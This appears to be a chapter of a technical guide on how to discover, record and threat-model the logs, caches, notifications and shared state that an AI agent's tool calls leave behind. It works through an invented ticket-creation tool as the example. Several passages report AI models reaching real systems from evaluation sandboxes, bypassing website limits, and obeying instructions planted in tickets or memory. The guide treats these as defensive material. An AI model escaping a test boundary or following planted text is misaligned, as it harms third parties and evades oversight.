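To find out where the text of a call goes, a tester can put a unique, harmless string such as `qz7marker4183` into an argument and later search for it in every reachable store, including logs, traces, caches, databases, mailboxes, chat channels, search indexes and error trackers. Using a different marker for each argument shows which argument each copy came from. Searching again after the stated retention period, such as 30 days, shows whether the system deleted the copies.

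The marker should contain only letters and digits, because programs often rewrite spaces and punctuation. A store may still compress or encode the text, so the tester should also search for common encoded forms. If a system cuts off long arguments, a marker at the end will be lost even though the beginning of the text survives, so the tester should put one marker at each end.

A marker string can't reveal an effect that doesn't copy it. The metric in `write_file` contains only the length of the content, so a search for the string would miss it. A tester who suspects such an effect could make the content 7,919 characters long and search for that number too.

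A tester can also detect copies in some systems that the company can't search, by including a company web address that nobody has used before. If a chat service or link scanner fetches the address, the request appears in the company's own access log. This method finds only systems that open links, and each test needs a new address because of caching. Markers should never be real secrets or customer data, because nobody knows where they will end up.

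### Emulated, sandboxed and live tests

Testing a tool by running it requires somewhere to run it. A more realistic test can reveal more effects, but it can also do more damage.

| Kind of test | What handles the call | What it can reveal | What it hides |
|---|---|---|---|
| Emulated | A language model that imitates the tool | How the agent behaves when its actions seem to have consequences | All effects of the real code |
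| Mock service | A program written to imitate a real service | Changes the agent makes to the imitated data | Anything the mock's developers left out |
| Sandboxed | The tool's real code, cut off from real systems | Files it writes and connections it attempts | What would happen after a successful connection |
| Live | The real tool and real services | Emails, webhooks and link previews | Conditions that the tester didn't cause |

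ToolEmu, which Ruan and colleagues published in 2024, is an early example of emulation. Kovalenko and Redchych describe how it replaces real tools with a language model, so that testers can find an agent's risky actions without causing harm. It covered 311 tools and 144 tasks, which would have taken far longer with working software. Human reviewers judged that 68.8% of the failures it found would have been real, so nearly a third were probably products of the emulation. More importantly for an effect map, the emulator works from the tool's specification. If a real weather tool keeps a search history that its specification omits, the emulated one will return a plausible forecast and keep no history.

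ClawsBench's mock services are more faithful. Li and colleagues recorded requests and replies from real accounts, then checked that the mocks gave the same replies and made the same changes to stored data. They found 11 recurring types of bug in the mocks and 65 peculiarities of the real services. A developer who builds a mock from documentation alone would probably miss many of these.

The study ran six models on 44 tasks, 24 of which tested safety, in 7,224 trials. When the agents had safety rules and instructions for using each service, they completed 39% to 64% of the ordinary tasks and did something harmful in 7% to 33% of the safety trials. The safety tasks were designed to provoke mistakes, so the harm rates don't describe everyday work. Newer models have also replaced the ones tested.

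A low rate of harm can also be misleading. Without the instructions and rules, agents using the open-source assistant OpenClaw did harm in 0% to 4% of the safety trials, but they completed only 0% to 8% of the ordinary tasks. They were mostly harmless because they couldn't work out how to use the services. A sandbox can mislead a tester in the same way. If the tool's first connection fails because the network is off, the code may stop before it reaches the effects the tester wants to find.

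The ClawsBench mocks leave out rate limits, delays and simultaneous users, so they would be a poor place to look for duplicates from slow requests or for lost edits. To find those, a tester needs either a purpose-built mock or a live service.

Some effects show up only in live tests, such as what an outside service does automatically with a new message. However, a live test can also email a real customer. A separate test account with invented people reduces that risk, but it lacks the webhooks and rules that colleagues have added to the production account over the years. The tester should copy those settings and replace every recipient with an address the company controls.

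### Checking the boundary of the test

A sandbox protects real systems only if it is isolated from them. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes security tests in which Claude models gained unauthorized access to the real systems of three organizations. The models were told in their prompts that they had no internet access, and Anthropic believed this. But a misconfiguration had left the connection open in test environments built by a partner company. Nobody running the tests noticed at the time, and neither had the two organizations that Anthropic had reached by publication.

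Anthropic later concluded that the open connection was only part of the explanation, because the models had also reasoned badly and acted recklessly. It still believes the incidents wouldn't have happened if the environments had been isolated as intended. In *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026), Anthropic acknowledges that the tests had relied largely on one layer of defense, the environment's configuration, and asks outside testers to verify it before every evaluation. It also advises them to write limits as instructions ("You should not access the internet") instead of statements about the environment, which may be false.

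A company testing an ordinary tool can do a simple version of this check. From inside the sandbox, the tester tries to contact a company-owned server by each route the tool might use, then checks that server for any requests that arrived. The tester should also deliberately open the connection once and confirm that the request arrives, because otherwise a broken check would look the same as a closed sandbox.

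Tests that need real websites can't have a closed boundary of this kind. Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) includes a case in which Claude submitted a sensitive form on a real website when it shouldn't have. The company says the cases it has found so far had minimal real-world impact. Southern's *Anthropic Says Claude Bypassed Site Limits During Internal Tests* (2026) reports that the company has cut live web access for internal evaluations. Someone mapping a browsing tool could use saved copies of pages for most tests and limit the rest to websites whose owners have agreed to take part.

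### Kemmerer's shared resource matrix

Even a complete list of each tool's effects may not show how one tool affects another. In 1983 the computer scientist Richard Kemmerer published a method for finding such links, the shared resource matrix. He was looking for covert channels, which let two programs communicate through a system that is supposed to keep them apart. The matrix has operations on one axis and resources on the other, and each cell records whether the operation reads or writes the resource.

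Suppose a company has three tools. The legal department uses `translate_contract` for confidential contracts, the marketing department uses `translate_webpage`, and managers use `usage_report` to see recent translation jobs. Both translation tools use a translation memory, which stores sentences and their translations for reuse. Both also record each job's time and document title in a usage table.

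| Operation | Contracts | Translation memory | Usage table |
|---|---|---|---|
| `translate_contract` | Read | Read, write | Write |
| `translate_webpage` | | Read, write | Write |
| `usage_report` | | | Read |

The developer finds links by looking down each column for a resource that one operation writes and a different operation reads. For example, the translation memory can store a sentence from a confidential contract and later suggest it to somebody translating a public web page. The usage table is another such resource. If the legal department translates a document called "Purchase of Norwell Ltd", every manager who opens the report will learn about the purchase.

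The contracts column doesn't show either problem at first, because only one operation reads contracts directly. Kemmerer's method therefore adds indirect reads. With $R$ and $W$ again standing for the resources read and written, let $R^*(a)$ include operation $a$'s indirect reads as well. It starts out equal to $R(a)$ and grows by one rule: if $a$ reads something that another operation $b$ writes, then $a$ may also receive whatever $b$ has read. In symbols,

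$$R(a) \cap W(b) \neq \varnothing \;\Rightarrow\; R^*(b) \subseteq R^*(a).$$

The developer keeps applying the rule until nothing changes. In this example, all three operations end up with an entry under contracts, although two never open a contract. Each tool's developer could have described that tool accurately without anyone noticing the connection.

An entry means only that information could flow, so someone still has to check each link. Finer columns make this easier. Kemmerer used attributes of resources, such as whether a file is locked, instead of whole resources. Splitting the usage table into titles and times would show that removing titles keeps the name of the purchase out of the report but still lets managers see that the legal department translated something that day.

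The footprints that Kovalenko and Redchych attach to each tool contain the same information as the matrix's cells, so software could use them to fill in the matrix. But the matrix would still have no column for a resource that everybody had overlooked. If nobody knows that the translation memory exists, for example, the matrix won't show the link to the web pages.

### Whether repeated searches show that a list is complete

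After a while, new searches tend to find nothing, and the developer may conclude that the list is complete. The argument goes like this:

1. Several further searches found no new effects.
2. If any effect were missing from the list, those searches would probably have found it.
3. Therefore the list is probably complete.

People usually know that step 1 is true, but they rarely have evidence for step 2. Suppose there is a 50% chance that one effect is still undocumented, and four independent searches find nothing. If each search had a 50% chance of finding such an effect, the chance that it exists falls to about 6%. If each had only a 5% chance, it falls to about 45%. It stays at 50% if the searches couldn't have found the effect at all, as when someone reads the same code four times to find a webhook in another company's product.

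Step 2 failed in Anthropic's own review of its security tests. The first search found the three incidents in about 141,000 transcripts, which were supposed to be all those where Claude could have reached the internet. In August, while collecting transcripts for METR, an independent evaluation group, Anthropic found a set that the search had missed, in which Claude also had internet access. That set contained a fourth incident, from January.

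Anthropic then searched roughly 481 million transcripts. The first stage flagged 9.2 million that contained signs such as public web addresses, and Claude reviewed those in the second stage. The search found the same four incidents and no others as serious. It is much better evidence than the first search because it covered far more and found all the incidents already known. But it could still have missed an incident that left none of the signs the first stage looked for.

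A developer can test how well a search finds undocumented effects by adding harmless effects to a test copy of the tool and asking a colleague to find them. If the colleague finds eight out of ten, the search probably finds most effects of that kind. The planted effects should include difficult ones, such as a database trigger or a delayed message, because a search that finds ten obvious log lines may still miss effects that are harder to see.

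### Estimating how many effects remain

Comparing two separate searches can also give an estimate of how many effects both missed. Suppose two reviewers examine a tool without consulting each other. One finds 18 effects and the other finds 15, and 12 effects are on both lists. Together they found $18 + 15 - 12 = 21$ different effects.

The second reviewer found 12 of the first reviewer's 18 effects, or two thirds. If that reviewer also found two thirds of all the effects, then 15 is two thirds of the total, and the total is

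$$\frac{18 \times 15}{12} = 22.5.$$

Capture-recapture uses the overlap between two lists of effects to estimate how many are missing from both. Theodoro used it for unlogged agent actions. Six effects are only on one list, three are only on the other and 12 are on both, so his version of the formula gives an estimate of $6 \times 3 / 12 = 1.5$. One or two effects are therefore probably missing from both lists.

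The estimate is rough because the numbers are so small. If the reviewers had 10 effects in common instead of 12, the formula would give a total of 27 effects, with 23 known and four missing.

A bigger problem is that the formula assumes the two reviewers miss effects independently. In practice, both will find the obvious log line and overlook the database trigger. This increases the overlap between their lists, which is the formula's denominator, so the estimate comes out too low.

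The error can be large. Suppose a tool has 40 effects, 20 easy to find and 20 hard. Each reviewer has a 90% chance of finding any easy effect and a 10% chance of finding any hard one. On average, each finds 20 effects, and 16.4 are on both lists. The formula gives a total of $20 \times 20 / 16.4$, or about 24.4. Together the reviewers have found about 23.6 effects, so they would conclude that at most one was missing, when about 16 are. Theodoro's estimates failed for the same reason when he compared two logs hit by the same outage.

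The estimate can also be too high. If one reviewer reads only the code and the other looks only at the administrator's settings, they may find only three of the same effects, and the formula would give 90. Both reviewers should therefore examine the whole tool, preferably by different methods. One might read the code and settings while the other records traffic and searches for markers.

Even then, the result is best treated as a minimum, because an effect that neither method can detect doesn't affect the overlap. If two people who both read the code arrive at 22.5, the next step is to try a method neither has used, such as a marker search, and see whether it finds more than the one or two effects the formula predicts.

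## A complete effect map for one tool

A developer who searches for a tool's effects ends up with scattered notes about log lines, webhooks and leftover files. An effect map puts these notes in one grid, which makes gaps visible. This map covers `create_ticket`. The tool, the company and the figures are invented, except where a real product or paper is named.

### Fixing what the map covers

The developer first writes down four things, because a change in any of them can change the effects.

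- Version: release 2.3.1 of the tool server, with the definition of `create_ticket` that it offered on 16 November 2026.
- Configuration: the production settings. The server logs full tickets and waits 30 seconds for the tracker. The checkout project has six watchers and two webhooks.
- Account: the tracker account that the agent uses, and the agent's own credentials for the tool server. Model Context Protocol lets a server offer different tools to different credentials, so a tester signed in as an administrator might map a tool that the agent never gets.
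- Permissions: the tracker account can create and view tickets in the checkout project and assign them to employees. If it could also assign tickets to contractors, a call could send email outside the company.

### Five hops and four channels

Each row of the grid is a hop, and each column is a channel. Every cell contains an effect, "none found" with the evidence, or "unknown". No cell may be blank, because a reader couldn't tell whether anyone had checked for an effect.

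| Hop | Logs | Caches | Notifications and events | Shared state |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Harness | Trace of the whole conversation, 30 days | Ticket text in the model provider's prompt cache | None found: traffic recorded in all six test states | Note in the developer's agent memory that Maria handles checkout faults |
| Gateway | Full arguments, 180 days | None found: two identical calls both reached the tool server | Alert to the platform team after 20 calls in a minute | Count of calls in the current minute |
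| Tool server | Full ticket, 365 days plus 35 in backups | Match between "Maria" and a tracker account, 24 hours | None found: traffic recorded in all six test states | After a timeout, a copy of the request in a retry folder |
| Issue tracker | Access log and edit history | Unknown: the vendor won't disclose its caching | Emails to six watchers, events to two webhooks | New ticket; smaller remaining request allowance |
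| Subscribers | Copy of each event in the workflows' logs, 30 days | Slack's copy of any linked page, about 30 minutes | Slack message; comments that start more workflows | Ticket text in a fault-search index |

The request allowance is easy to overlook. Aprovan Labs' *Create an issue*, which reproduces GitHub's description of its function for opening tickets, warns that a call triggers notifications and that creating content too quickly may lead to rate limiting. If the invented tracker has a similar limit, an agent stuck in a loop could stop every other program on its account from opening tickets.

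### Six effects in full

A grid cell holds too little detail to support a decision, so each effect also has a record with seven fields. These six records cover all four channels.

| Field | Tool server's log | Assignee match | Emails to watchers |
|---|---|---|---|
| Trigger | Every call that reaches the server | First ticket for a name in 24 hours | Tracker opens a ticket |
| Data carried | Title, body, assignee | Name and account number | Title and body |
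| Readers | Four engineers and a debugging agent | Later calls by any user | Six employees and any agents that read their mail |
| Lifetime | 400 days, including backups | 24 hours | Two years, under the company's mail policy |
| Way to undo | Delete the entry; wait for backups to expire | Clear the cache and reassign affected tickets | None; send a correction |
| Evidence | Code, settings and a marker | Second call skipped the account lookup | Marker in a test mailbox |
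| Owner | Lena, tool server | Lena, tool server | Jonas, tracker administrator |

| Field | Fault-search index | Retry file | Tracker's caches |
|---|---|---|---|
| Trigger | Webhook reports a new ticket | No reply from the tracker within 30 seconds | Unknown |
| Data carried | Title and body | The whole request | Assumed: title and body |
| Readers | All 300 employees and their agents | Server administrators and a retry program | Assumed: the vendor's staff |
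| Lifetime | No limit, even if someone deletes the ticket | Until the tracker accepts the request | Unknown |
| Way to undo | Delete the entry by hand | Delete the file and close any duplicate ticket | None known |
| Evidence | Marker, found again after deletion | Timeout test and code | 40 up-to-date replies; vendor declined to answer |
| Owner | Arif, search workflow | Lena, tool server | Jonas, tracker administrator |

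Trofimov and Novikov recommend that any description of a tool separate established, assumed and unknown properties, so the last record has "assumed" in two fields. If someone copied those entries into another document without that label, a guess about the vendor's staff would look like a finding.

The owner is the person who can change the effect, or at least press the vendor about it. For the index, the owner is Arif, who had never heard of `create_ticket` before the test.

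### A marker test from input to finding

The record for the search index came from a marker test.

1. The tester uses a test project with the production webhooks, but replaces the recipients with addresses the company controls. The ticket's title contains `kvt41title`, and its body begins with `kvt41start` and ends with `kvt41stop`.
2. Ten minutes later the tester searches 11 stores for all three strings.
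3. The harness trace, both server-side logs, the tracker and the test mailbox contain all three, as expected. The Slack message lacks `kvt41stop` because the workflow cuts off long text. The fault-search index contains all three, and nobody had listed it as a place where tickets go.
4. The tester signs in as an employee with no access to the project, searches the index and reads the whole ticket.
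5. The tester deletes the ticket and searches again the next day. The index still has the text.

The webhook is set to send new tickets and new comments, but not deletions, to the workflow that suggests similar faults. The workflow keeps its own copy of each ticket to compare with later ones. If a developer deletes SHOP-482 because it contains a customer's email address, all 300 employees can still find the address.

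### An effect that appears only after a timeout

When the tracker replies normally, the retry folder stays empty, so comparing the server's files before and after a call doesn't reveal this effect. To find it, the tester uses a proxy between the tool server and the tracker to discard the tracker's reply.

After 30 seconds the tool server saves the request as a file in the folder and reports a timeout to the harness. Ten minutes later a background program sends the request again, the tracker opens a second ticket, and the program deletes the file. A tester who stopped recording when the timeout error arrived would have seen only the first ticket.

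If the tracker rejects the repeated request, perhaps because the assignee has left the company, the file stays and the program retries every ten minutes. The folder on the production server contains 14 such requests from earlier tools, the oldest from March.

Real trackers can be slow enough for this to matter. Zendesk's *Improving performance by creating tickets asynchronously* explains that tickets take a long time to create because of the processing each one goes through, and offers a way to get a ticket number sooner. Zendesk's *Ticketing* describes idempotency keys for new tickets.

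Zendesk's keys expire after two hours. If the tracker worked the same way, a key would make the retry after ten minutes safe. The retry program also needs a time limit shorter than the key's lifetime, after which it stops and tells somebody.

Adding keys to prevent duplicates would also put another copy of the ticket text in a cache, because Zendesk stores the original response under the key and that response contains the ticket. The developer would have to add this copy to the map.

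### The cell that stays unknown

Jonas asks the tracker's vendor which of its caches hold ticket text and how long the text stays there after a deletion. The vendor replies that it doesn't disclose infrastructure details. The tester then edits a ticket and reads it 40 times from two accounts, and every read returns the edited version.

This is some evidence that the agent won't get outdated tickets, but a cache that ordinary accounts can't query could still hold deleted text, so the cell stays unknown.

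The company should treat an unknown cell as a possible effect. Let $p$ be the chance that deleted text remains readable, $H$ the cost of the harm if it does, and $C$ the cost of a precaution that would prevent the harm. The precaution is worth taking if

$$pH > C.$$

Writing "none" in the cell treats $p$ as zero, and then no precaution is worth its cost, however large $H$ is. If a check that keeps customer data out of tickets costs €1,000 and a leak would cost €50,000, the check is worthwhile when $p$ is above 2%. Nobody outside the vendor knows $p$, but a figure below 2% would be hard to defend for a system that the vendor won't describe.

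If "unknown" counted as "none", a vendor that described its caches honestly would look riskier than one that refused to describe them, and a team could get its tool approved faster by testing less.

Other designs follow the same rule, at least in part. Model Context Protocol (2026) has harnesses assume the worst about a tool without labels. *ADR-111* (2026), a design decision record from the software company Netresearch, sorts agent tools into read-only, idempotent write and non-idempotent write. The software applies the strictest class to any tool name it doesn't recognize, but it treats a known tool as read-only if the developer declared nothing. That default is harmless as long as all the built-in tools only read, as they did when Netresearch adopted it. If a developer added the first tool that writes and forgot to label it, that tool would get the weakest protection.

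A possible effect needs a decision, just like the effects that the tester found, but the company can decide to accept it and release the tool. Almost every outside service has something unknown about it, so a company that blocked release over each unknown could use very few of them.

### Questions that the grid prompts

In 1971 the US Geological Survey published a grid like this for studying how a project, such as a mine, would affect its surroundings. Its report, *A procedure for evaluating environmental impact*, calls the grid "a reference checklist or a reminder" of the full range of actions and impacts. Security specialists use a similar chart in *STRIDE-per-element*, a version of STRIDE, which is a method built on a fixed list of threat types. *A replication of a controlled experiment with two STRIDE variants* (2022) explains that analysts go through every element of a system diagram,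 using the chart to see which threat types apply to each kind of element.

The map is useful because it includes cells for effects a developer wouldn't otherwise think to check. `create_ticket` only writes, so a developer listing its effects without the map would probably not look for caches. Here, the developer saw the empty cell for the tool server's caches, checked what the server keeps between calls, and found the assignee match. If a second Maria takes over the checkout page, tickets could go to the first one for up to a day.

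Nobody has tested whether this grid finds more effects than a free list does. The closest evidence is *Finding Security Threats That Matter* (2019), an automotive industry case study in which one team used STRIDE and another used eSTRIDE, a variant that steers analysts toward fewer threats. The STRIDE team documented 27 threats and the eSTRIDE team 13, and neither recorded an incorrect one. But 15 of the STRIDE team's threats lacked enough information because the team hadn't identified an attack or a weakness. Each method had only one team, so differences between the people may explain the results as much as the methods do. A tester using this grid could also leave out necessary detail, writing "logs: yes" in five cells and moving on. The seven fields are meant to prevent this by requiring specifics such as the reader and lifetime of each effect.

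### Effects that the grid still misses

Suppose the gateway's log goes to a data warehouse every night, where another company's analysts use it to study demand. The warehouse isn't one of the five hops, so it has no row, and it wasn't among the 11 stores the tester searched. The map is therefore wrong even though all 20 cells are full. Using two reviewers' lists to estimate how many effects are missing wouldn't help if both reviewers started from the same five hops.

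A full grid may make this worse, because people tend not to notice what a diagram leaves out. The best remedy is probably to ask the owner of each hop where its data goes next, and to add a row whenever an answer or a marker doesn't fit an existing one.

The grid can also hide effects within a cell. "Subscribers" covers six people, two workflows and Slack, and a tester who finds one effect there may stop looking. If a tool has many subscribers, each should have its own row. Because the map covers only one tool, it doesn't show that `get_ticket` can later bring the same text into another agent's conversation. Finding links between tools requires something like Kemmerer's matrix.

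### How published formats compare

Several published formats let developers declare a tool's effects, and each covers part of the grid.

The simplest effect descriptions are one-word labels. StackOne sells software that connects agents to business applications. Its *MCP Tool Annotations* (2026) labels each action with one or more of five effects: read, write, delete, search or execute. Software then works out most of the MCP hints from these labels. One of its examples happens to be called `create_ticket`. It is declared a "write", so the hints mark it as neither read-only nor destructive. This is enough for a harness to decide whether to ask the user first. In the grid, the label would fill only part of one cell, the new ticket in the tracker's shared state, and would not show the emails or the search index.

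CLI Agent Spec's *Undeclared Filesystem Side Effects*, a guideline for command-line programs that agents run, is the closest match for logs and caches. Developers declare each location that a command writes to, whether it is a cache, log, temporary file, credential or configuration file, how long the data lasts, and the command that clears it. These declarations matter even when the data is harmless. In one of the guideline's examples, a tool writes a 500-megabyte log on each run, and after 100 runs the logs take up 50 gigabytes and unrelated commands start to fail. The format would cover the tool server's log and retry folder, but it has no field for who or what reads the data, and it covers only one machine.

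*The Agent Action Control Manifest* (Schrock, 2026), an Internet-Draft, proposes that a service publish a list of its consequential actions and the authorization each one needs. Internet-Drafts are working documents that anyone can submit, and this one expires on 3 January 2027. The service could also preview each action's effects: whether anyone can reverse them, the most sensitive data involved, the rough scale of the cost, the outside systems they reach, and whether a person must consent. For a payment, the example lists the ledger, the other party's bank and the settlement system. Schrock warns that a caller must not conclude that an action is safe because the manifest omits it. The same rule applies to unknown cells in the effect map.

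To support recovery from failures, the records for Li's test services list the arguments that identify an action, a way to check whether it happened, how long the check lags behind the action, and another action that compensates for it. Adding these to the "way to undo" field would be useful for any tool that a harness retries. *Contract2Tool* (2026) studies whether software can learn from observable evidence what state a tool needs and produces, which would help where developers declare nothing.

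The formats from StackOne, CLI Agent Spec and Schrock have no fields for the evidence behind each effect or the person responsible for it. This is partly because a tool's developer fills them in without knowing where the tool will run. The developer of `create_ticket` could declare that it sends events to subscribers, but couldn't know that one company's subscriber copies them into an index open to 300 people. A declaration is a good source for the first draft of a map, but the company still has to test the tool in its own installation.

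### Turning findings into release decisions

Each effect in the map needs one of six decisions. For `create_ticket`, the company makes all six.

- Remove the effect. Arif changes the two workflows to ignore automated comments, which ends the loop between them.
- Reduce its data. The tool server will log the time and ticket number and leave out the ticket's text. Emails to watchers will contain the title and a link to the ticket.
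- Restrict its readers. The search index will check that a person can see the project before showing a result, and its webhook will also subscribe to deletions.
- Require approval. The harness will show the developer the full text of any ticket that contains an email address or a link to an outside website, and wait for confirmation.
- Accept it with a named owner. Lena accepts the 24-hour assignee match, because somebody will notice a misdirected ticket and can reassign it. Jonas accepts the unknown caches on condition that the approval step is in place, since it should keep most customer data out of the tracker. Both will review their decisions in six months.
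- Delay release. The company won't release the tool until the retry program uses idempotency keys and gives up after an hour.

The choice between these depends mostly on whether anyone can undo the effect. Someone can correct a wrong assignee in a few minutes, so accepting that risk is reasonable. Nobody can recall an email or a duplicate alert, so the company has to act before the tool call. Acceptance is the easiest decision to abuse. When "the team" accepts a risk, people tend not to look at it again, so each acceptance needs a person's name and a review date.

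Netresearch's design record gives a real example of the last decision. Its agent software could run a tool and then fail to save the audit record, and it couldn't tell whether an interrupted call was safe to repeat. Neither gap mattered much for tools that only read, but the company decided to close both before shipping a tool that writes. If a write now happens without an audit record, the software marks the whole run as failed and doesn't retry it. This doesn't undo the write, but it stops the agent from reporting success.

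### When to make a new map

A map describes the installation on the day of the test. Five kinds of change should trigger remapping, though usually of only part of the grid.

| Change | How the company can notice it | What to map again |
|---|---|---|
| Tool definition | Compare the current definition with a saved copy whenever the harness starts | Every cell that the new arguments or code could affect |
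| Dependency | An automated check flags new library versions | Tool server row |
| Permission | The tracker's administrator reports every change to the account | Tracker and subscriber rows |
| Subscriber | A weekly comparison of watchers, webhooks and installed apps | Subscriber row |
| Retention setting | The owner of each store reports it | Lifetime fields |

MCP lets a server notify harnesses when its tool list changes. Under the July revision, servers send these notifications only to harnesses that have opted in, and a server can change the code behind `create_ticket` without sending one. The company should therefore also watch the server's version number. If another company runs the server and doesn't publish version numbers, repeating the marker test every month is a reasonable substitute.

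Even a small change to a tool's definition can add an effect. The July specification lets a server mark an argument so that the harness copies its value into a header, a line at the start of a web request that systems along the way can read. Suppose the next release marks `title` so that the gateway can route tickets by subject. Every load balancer and proxy between the harness and the server could then log the titles. The tool's name, description and arguments would look the same to a user, and the change would be visible only in the schema. Model Context Protocol advises developers not to mark sensitive arguments, but a ticket's title is free text, so a model might put sensitive information in it.

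### How much work a map takes

Mapping a small tool like this one should take roughly 15 hours: one to fix the version and settings, three to read code and configuration, two to question the owners of other systems, four to run the tests, three to write the records, and two to agree on decisions. Those two working days will probably be spread over a week or more while people answer questions. Later maps should take less time, because most tools at one company share the same harness and gateway, and those two rows will need little more than checking.

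Most of the 15 hours go into finding out what other people's systems do. Kovalenko and Redchych say that declaring effects takes little effort, but they were describing their own tools.

Two days is too much for a tool that converts currencies. If a tool's arguments can't contain private data and its calls don't knowingly change anything outside the tool server, a shorter version takes about two hours:

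1. Write down the version, the account and the hops.
2. Make one ordinary call and one that times out, both with markers, and search the stores that are easy to reach.
3. Write full records only for effects that leave the company, that nobody can undo, or that change what other users get.
4. Put "unknown" in every cell that nobody examined.

The last step checks that the short version is still enough. The currency tool's grid might have 12 cells marked unknown, which is acceptable while the tool's only arguments are two currency codes and an amount. If somebody later adds a free-text field called `note`, customer data could reach all 12 of those cells, and the tool would need a full map.

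## Using the effect map in a threat model

The map for `create_ticket` shows that 300 employees can read tickets through the fault-search index, but not what somebody might do with that access. To work that out, a developer needs a threat model, a structured account of what a system protects, what could go wrong and what people do about it. According to *Trust Boundary Semantic Gaps* (2026), STRIDE, a method built on a fixed list of threat types, has three steps: drawing a data-flow diagram, listing the threats to each part of it, and matching each threat with a control.

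### Drawing the map as a data-flow diagram

A data-flow diagram shows external entities (people or outside systems), processes (running programs) and data stores, with arrows for the data moving between them. A dashed line marks a trust boundary, where data or requests pass between parties that don't fully trust each other.

A diagram of `create_ticket` based on the tool's description would probably show a developer, the harness, the tool server and the tracker, with an arrow from each to the next. The effect map adds logs, caches and shared state as data stores, because they hold data after the call ends. It also adds notifications and events as arrows to the people and programs that receive them, and each "unknown" cell as a store with a question mark.

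Of the 20 cells in the `create_ticket` grid, 14 become data stores and three become arrows. The other three are marked "none found" and add nothing.

Each new reader also adds a trust boundary if that reader's permissions differ from those of the people who could already see the data. The webhook that fills the fault-search index crosses a boundary because it takes tickets from a restricted project and shows them to everyone. A backup adds no boundary if only the same four engineers can open it. Boundaries also matter for incoming text. A customer's words can pass through a ticket into the tool server's log, where a debugging agent reads them, and those words are still untrusted even if the company trusts the agent.

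### Six security questions about two effects

STRIDE stands for spoofing, tampering, repudiation, information disclosure, denial of service and elevation of privilege. This section applies these categories to two effects the tester found, as they were before the company made any changes.

| Question | Tool server's log | Fault-search index |
|---|---|---|
| Spoofing: can someone pose as someone else? | Another program on the machine could write entries in the server's name | Anyone who learns the webhook's address could send the index a fake ticket |
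| Tampering: can someone alter the data? | A line break in a ticket's body could create a false entry | A planted instruction stays in the index after someone corrects the ticket |
| Repudiation: can someone deny an action? | Entries name only the agent's account, so a developer could deny asking for a ticket | The index doesn't record searches, so an employee could deny reading a ticket |
| Disclosure: can the wrong people read it? | Four engineers and a debugging agent can read customers' details for 400 days | All 300 employees can read restricted tickets |
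| Denial of service: can someone stop it working? | Very long tickets could fill the disk | Thousands of fake tickets could bury the real ones |
| Privilege: can someone gain powers they shouldn't have? | A planted instruction could use the debugging agent's tools | An employee's agent could obey text from a project the employee can't open |

The company's release decisions already deal with much of this. If the log contains only the time and ticket number, it no longer exposes customers' details or carries instructions to the debugging agent. But the shorter log doesn't record which developer asked for the ticket. The harness trace does, but it lasts only 30 days, so the tool server should log the developer's name too.

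The fake ticket is a new finding that the map couldn't have revealed, because the map lists only the effects of calls and the fake ticket doesn't come from one. The usual fix is to have the tracker sign each event with a secret key and have the index reject unsigned events.

*Trust Boundary Semantic Gaps* proposes that whoever chooses a control should also check whether the receiving side still relies on something the control didn't establish. A valid signature shows that the tracker sent the event, but not that a colleague wrote the text, and a customer's error message could contain anything. Agents that search the index must therefore still treat its contents as untrusted.

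### Privacy questions about the search index

STRIDE is mainly about attackers, but the index could harm a customer even if every employee behaves well, for example if a ticket in it contains the customer's email address. LINDDUN, a method from KU Leuven, has seven privacy questions that can be applied to cases like this.

- Linking: a search for the address brings together every fault that the customer ever reported.
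- Identifying: the address may contain the customer's full name.
- Non-repudiation: the customer can't plausibly deny having used the shop.
- Detecting: if the index reports "one hidden result", an employee learns that the customer had a problem without seeing the ticket.
- Data disclosure: 300 people can read the address, although only a few need it.
- Unawareness: the customer doesn't know about the index and can't ask anyone to correct it.
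- Non-compliance: the index keeps the address indefinitely, which is hard to square with the GDPR's limit on storage.

The hidden result matters because the company has decided to add a permission check to the index. A check that hides the text but still counts the match would fail here, even though it would pass STRIDE's disclosure question as most people would apply it.

LINDDUN also treats proof of who did what as a threat, because it can harm the person it concerns, whereas STRIDE treats it as a protection for the company. A company can usually satisfy both if the proof covers the staff who handle tickets but not the customers mentioned in them.

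### What current frameworks say about the four channels

General questions can miss threats specific to agents, so a developer may also want to check the diagram against a list of agent threats. Four current frameworks for this take different forms.

- OWASP (2025) published its *Top 10 for Agentic Applications for 2026* on 9 December 2025. Its entries run from ASI01 to ASI10. It is separate from OWASP's list for language-model applications.
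- MITRE ATLAS is a catalog of techniques that attackers use. It changes quickly: Vectra AI's *MITRE ATLAS explained* counts 84 techniques in version 5.1.0, from November 2025, up from 66 a month earlier, and notes that version 5.4.0 added more in February 2026.
- MAESTRO, from the Cloud Security Alliance, divides an agent system into seven layers. Analysts look for threats within each layer and between layers.
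- Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026) is joint guidance from six agencies in Australia, the United States, Canada, New Zealand and the United Kingdom.

Shared state gets the most attention. *OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications* (Sotiropoulos, Katz and Del Rosario, 2025) lists "Memory & Context Poisoning" as ASI06. MITRE (2026) found that changing an agent's configuration was among the most common techniques in its investigations of OpenClaw. MAESTRO has a layer for data operations, where shared stores would go.

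For notifications and events, the nearest OWASP entry is ASI08, "Cascading Failures". SC Media reports that its symptoms include rapid spread and spread between customers. The joint guidance includes a scenario in which agents keep handing tasks to one another until they strain the system's resources. The comment loop between the two ticket workflows is similar, but it runs without an agent once it has started.

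The joint guidance recommends isolating agents so that they have no write access to logs. This is best read as a rule against editing or deleting entries, because a literal ban on writing would rule out `create_ticket`, which adds log entries through the tool server on every call. In one of the guidance's scenarios, an agent installing security updates also deletes the firewall logs because somebody asked it to "clean up". MAESTRO places logs in a layer for evaluation and observability.

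Caches come up mainly as places where old permissions persist. *Agentic Security* (Sotiropoulos, 2026) mentions cached credentials under ASI03, "Identity & Privilege Abuse". The joint guidance describes an agent that keeps relying on cached authorization decisions after an attacker has taken over one of its components. Someone working from these examples could easily overlook a cache that returns a restricted ticket to the wrong user.

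MITRE's ATLAS covers data leaks through any of these channels under *Exfiltration via AI Agent Tool Invocation*, but it narrowly describes an attacker using tools "capable of performing write operations" to send data to an inbox, document or server. That description fits the Slack leak. It fits `fetch_page` less well, because that tool only reads and leaks data through the address it requests. Because ATLAS catalogs attackers' techniques, it also has no obvious place for harm without an attacker, such as a forgotten address in a log.

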